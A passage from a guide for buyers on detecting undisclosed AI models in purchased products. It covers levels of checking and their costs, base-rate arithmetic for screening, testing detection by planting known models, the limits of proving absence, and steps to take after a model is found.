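|---|---|---|
| Blocking the developer's addresses | Stops direct use only | Stops only DeepSeek's own app and service |
| Searching the vendor's code and settings | Good, if the vendor cooperates | Good, unless someone has renamed the model |
| Checking cloud bills | Good, because somebody pays for each use | Works on a cloud platform that charges by model, but not on the vendor's own servers |
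| Blocking the model in the vendor's cloud account | Good, apart from uses through other accounts | Same on a cloud platform; no effect on the vendor's own servers |
| Comparing weights with published files | Not possible, because the weights aren't public | Good for exact copies, weak after changes |
| Fingerprinting the answers | A clue | A clue, weaker after heavy retraining |
| Asking the developer | May identify its direct customers | Little use, because it can't know who copied the weights |

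A vendor that runs a renamed DeepSeek model on its own servers may leave no trace in anyone else's records. The buyer can ask the vendor for the training records and the hash of the original download, which an honest one should be able to produce. If the vendor says it trained the model from scratch, its computing bills should be large enough to make that believable.

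## How much to check, and what a clean result shows

A buyer with a thousand products can't take each one apart, and doing so would waste money for most of them. US federal agencies had common rules for checking software security until January 2026, when Vought (2026) rescinded them in *Adopting a Risk-based Approach to Software and Hardware Security* and told each agency to match its checks to its own risks. Private buyers can also decide how much to check each product based on its risk.

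### Three levels of checking

How much a buyer should check depends on what the product can take in and what it can do. Whether staff expect it to contain AI is a bad guide. The University of Waterloo skipped its risk assessment of one product because staff didn't expect it to contain AI.

| Level | Checks | Products that justify it |
|---|---|---|
| Paper check | Supplier questions and an SBOM | Products with no sensitive data and no control over other systems, such as a warehouse label printer |
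| Technical check | The same, plus a file search and a network recording | Office software, devices with a camera or microphone, anything that handles staff or customer records |
| Full examination | The same, plus a teardown and several weeks of observation | Industrial controllers, equipment for secure rooms, very large orders, products from a supplier that has already given a false answer |

Someone should spend a few minutes looking for a camera or microphone on any device, even one that seems to need only a paper check. If it has either, the device needs a check at least one level higher.

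A technical check of an online service means studying its answers. Vought's memo also says that agencies wanting an SBOM for a cloud platform should ask for one that covers the "runtime production environment", meaning the software actually running. For the riskiest services, the buyer can ask for attestation or an independent review of the supplier's servers.

Singapore's security label for connected devices has similar levels. At the lower levels, the developer declares that the product meets the requirements. At the higher levels, an outside laboratory analyses the software and tries to break in, according to a presentation by the Cyber Security Agency of Singapore. The label covers security, so even a device with the top rating could contain an undisclosed model.

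### What the checks cost

Nobody appears to have published how much staff time a paper check takes. The computing for file searches is cheap. *RelicBOM* (Yu, Hu and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool that uses a language model to identify software components from the text left in compiled programs. It costs less than half a US cent per file, so a product with 2,000 program files would cost under $10 to analyze. Paying staff to investigate the matches would probably cost far more.

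The closest published figures for a full examination come from France, where laboratories evaluate the security of products within a fixed number of days. ANSSI, the French cybersecurity agency, set the basic workload at 25 person-days in 2011, according to the version history of its *First Level Security Certification For Information Technology Products* (2022). Bouffard's *Certification and IoT* (2019) gives a price of €25,000 to €35,000, and lists ten more days if the product uses cryptography. An evaluation under Common Criteria, an international scheme with no time limit, cost €60,000 to €200,000.

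These prices are only a rough guide. They are several years old, ANSSI's *Certification de sécurité de premier niveau* (2023) raised the maximum workload to 60 person-days, and the evaluators look for security weaknesses, not AI models. At €30,000, a full examination would have added more than €1,000 to the cost of each of Waterloo's 29 vending machines, but it would add only €6 per camera to an order of 5,000.

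### The arithmetic of screening

Suppose a buyer checks 1,000 products, of which 100 contain an undisclosed model. The check finds 90% of these and wrongly flags 5% of the other 900. These numbers are invented.

| | Flagged | Cleared | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Contains an undisclosed model | 90 | 10 | 100 |
| Does not | 45 | 855 | 900 |
| Total | 135 | 865 | 1,000 |

Two-thirds of the flagged products contain an AI model. Ten of the 865 products the check clears also contain one. A clean result therefore lowers the chance that a product contains a model from 10% to about 1.2%.

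The general formula for that last figure is:

```text
chance that a cleared product contains a model
    = p × (1 - d) / [p × (1 - d) + (1 - p) × (1 - f)]

p = share of all products that contain an undisclosed model
d = share of those products that the check finds
f = share of the other products that the check wrongly flags
```

The same check gives very different results when models are more or less common:

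| Products with a model, out of 1,000 | Flags | Share of flags that are right | Share of cleared products that still contain a model |
|---|---|---|---|
| 500 | 475 | 95% | 9.5% |
| 100 | 135 | 67% | 1.2% |
| 10 | About 59 | 15% | 0.1% |

When undisclosed models are rare, most flags are wrong. Axelsson (1999), in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection*, made this argument about software that looks for hackers, and concluded that false alarms were the limiting factor in its performance. *Detecting manipulations in microchips* (2023), from Ruhr University Bochum, describes a test in which researchers looked for differences between microscope images of computer chips and the design files. They wrongly flagged only 500 of more than 1.5 million circuit cells, or about one in 3,000. But there were only 40 real differences, of which they found 37, so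 about 93% of their flags were false.

A clean result is less reassuring when undisclosed models are common. In the top row, almost one in ten cleared products still contains a model, although the check is no worse. No one knows the true share of products with undisclosed models, so a buyer should try several values of *p* before deciding how much to rely on a clean result.

### Two checks with the same blind spot

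The buyer could run a second check on the 865 cleared products. If this check also finds 90% of models, and its misses are independent of the first check's, it should find nine of the remaining ten. But if both checks search for weights files and the ten products all use remote models, the second check would find none of them and could wrongly flag another 43 products.

Yu and colleagues give a real example of a shared blind spot, though for software components in general rather than AI models. Many tools can recognise only components on a reference list. The researchers collected 1,173 program files whose main components were missing from the lists of two such tools, then tested four existing tools on them. One identified three components and the others at most one each, so all four together would have found six at most. The researchers' own tool, which doesn't need a list, found 464. They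 chose the files to expose this weakness, so the existing tools would do much better on ordinary software.

Buying the second tool from another company may not help. In *An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming*, Knight and Leveson tested whether programs written separately by different people would fail independently. They found that several programs failed on the same inputs far more often than chance would predict.

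Checks work better together when they rely on different evidence, as a file search and a network recording do. Both miss a model running behind the supplier's own server, so the supplier's answers still matter. A questionnaire and an SBOM are a weaker pair, because a supplier that wants to hide a model can leave it out of both.

### Planting known models

A buyer can replace the invented 90% with a measured figure by hiding known models in test products and counting how many its staff find. It could do this as follows:

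1. Someone who won't take part in the search adds models to copies of software whose contents the buyer already knows.
2. That person varies the hiding places: a plain weights file, a renamed one, an encrypted one, a call to a remote service, a model that downloads after a week.
3. They mix these copies with unaltered ones, so that the test also measures false flags.
4. The staff search the whole batch with their usual methods and time limits.
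5. The buyer works out a separate detection rate for each hiding place.

Planting more models gives a more precise estimate of the detection rate. If staff find 18 of 20, the measured rate is 90%, but the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 68% to 99%. If they find 90 of 100, the range narrows to between 82% and 95%.

No one seems to have published such a test for undisclosed models, but airports have used the method for years. Their X-ray machines insert pictures of weapons and bombs into images of passengers' bags and record whether the screener notices. *Reliability and validity of threat image projection data* (Buser, Schwaninger and colleagues, 2025) analysed about 1.2 million of these tests at a European airport. Roughly 100 tests per screener gave a fairly reliable score, as long as the pictures were hard enough that screeners missed more than a tenth of them. The scores also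 predicted how well screeners detected real prohibited items that people tried to carry through security.

Planted models should be rare as well as hard to find. According to *Using Eye Movements to Understand how Security Screeners Search for Threats*, people find a smaller share of targets when 2% of images contain one than when 50% do. A buyer who plants models in half of the test products may therefore overestimate how well a check works, at least if it depends on a person's attention.

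DARPA, the US military's research agency, ran a contest that used planted flaws to compare AI systems that look for security holes. In the August 2025 final, seven teams' systems together found 54 of the 63 planted flaws, or 86%, according to DARPA's *AI Cyber Challenge marks pivotal inflection point for cyber defense* (2025). They also found 18 real flaws. The score is too old to be a good measure of current AI, but people designing a similar test can still learn from the contest.

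A competition score depends largely on which flaws the organisers choose. Zhang, Park and colleagues (2026) found in *SoK: DARPA's AI Cyber Challenge* that a standard testing technique could detect 34 of the 63 flaws on its own. A system may also report nothing because it has broken down. Two of the leading systems stopped working partway through the final, and some others failed on particular projects. To guard against this, a buyer can include a model that is easy to detect in every batch. If the scanner misses it, the buyer can't rely on the scanner's other clean results.

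A measured rate also applies only to the kinds of hiding place tested. In the chip experiment, the researchers had mostly swapped circuit cells without trying to find lookalikes. Dorschel, Walendy and colleagues (2026), in *Hardware Trojans from Invisible Inversions*, re-examined the images and found cells that look the same but perform opposite functions. They used such pairs to design a processor back door that this type of inspection would not reveal. Similarly, a buyer whose staff find every unencrypted weights file in a test still doesn't know whether they would find models that a supplier had encrypted.

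### Why testing can't prove absence

A model may not run during the test because it is triggered only by a date, a software update or a particular phrase. If the trigger is a string of eight lower-case letters, trying all of the roughly 209 billion possibilities at 1,000 per second would take more than six years. Accidental conditions can have the same effect. In the DARPA contest, one flaw crashed the program only on the second run, so systems that tried each input once discarded a correct answer.

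Testers also have to choose which setup to test. ANSSI's *Critères pour l'évaluation en vue d'une certification de sécurité de premier niveau* (2024) states that an evaluator can't test a product on every possible platform, and has the evaluator agree on one platform with the customer or arrange extra work. The choice matters for products like Chrome, which downloads its language model only to some computers.

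There is a mathematical limit too. In 1936 Alan Turing proved that no general procedure can decide, for every program, whether it will eventually stop. It follows that no procedure can decide, for every program, whether it will ever run a model:

1. Suppose a perfect checker existed.
2. Take any calculation that doesn't involve a model, and add a final instruction that runs a face classifier.
3. The combined program runs the classifier only if the calculation finishes.
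4. The checker's answer would therefore reveal whether the calculation finishes.
5. Turing proved that no procedure can do this for every calculation, so the perfect checker can't exist.

This result rules out a method that works on every program, but a careful examiner can still reach a correct answer about a particular one. In the example, a file search could find the classifier whether or not it ever ran. Turing's proof also assumes unlimited memory. A real device has a finite number of possible states, so in principle someone could check them all, but even a kilobyte of memory has more states than anyone could test.

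Some narrow kinds of absence are provable from the hardware, as with the thermostat that was too small for a language model. For most products, the buyer should record what the check covered instead of writing "no AI":

> We searched the files of version 4.2 and recorded its network traffic for 14 days. We found no model files and no direct connections to known AI services. We could not open two encrypted files, and we did not examine the supplier's servers.

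### What to do after finding a model

The steps below are in the usual order, but if the product may contain an agent that can change other systems, the buyer should isolate it first.

1. **Preserve the evidence.** Staff should record the product's version and the time of the discovery, copy the suspicious files, compute their hashes, and save logs and network recordings. They should also block updates, because an update could remove the model. Switching a device off erases its working memory, so a specialist may need to copy that beforehand.

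2. **Establish what it is and what it can reach.** The flag may be false, so someone needs to confirm that there is a model. They should then find out whether it is a classifier, a language model or part of an agent, what data it receives, where the results go, and which accounts and tools the software can use.

3. **Isolate it.** For a camera, this may just mean unplugging the network cable. An agent may run on someone else's server, so the buyer also has to cancel its passwords and access keys. Cutting off a medical device or an industrial controller can be dangerous, and the people who operate it should decide how to do so safely.

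4. **Ask the supplier.** "What does this file do, and who receives its output?" will get a better answer than an accusation. The buyer should include the file's name and hash, set a deadline, and ask whether other products contain the same model. If the buyer suspects deliberate concealment, it should secure the evidence and speak to a lawyer before contacting the supplier, which may be able to delete files remotely.

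5. **Notify where the law requires it.** An undisclosed model is not automatically a data breach, but one that sends customer records to an unauthorised company may have caused one. Under the EU's General Data Protection Regulation, an organisation generally has 72 hours after learning of a personal data breach to tell the regulator, unless the breach is unlikely to put people at risk. Contracts and other laws may set different deadlines.

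6. **Accept, disable or return the product.** A buyer can reasonably accept a model that predicts when a battery will finish charging, and add it to the inventory. It might keep a useful door camera but have the supplier disable the age estimator, then repeat the test that found it, both immediately and after the next update. If the supplier hid an agent with access to the buyer's systems, the buyer should normally return the product, after removing its own data and keeping copies of the evidence.

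Whatever it decides, the buyer should search its other products for the same file, since several manufacturers may have bought the same component.
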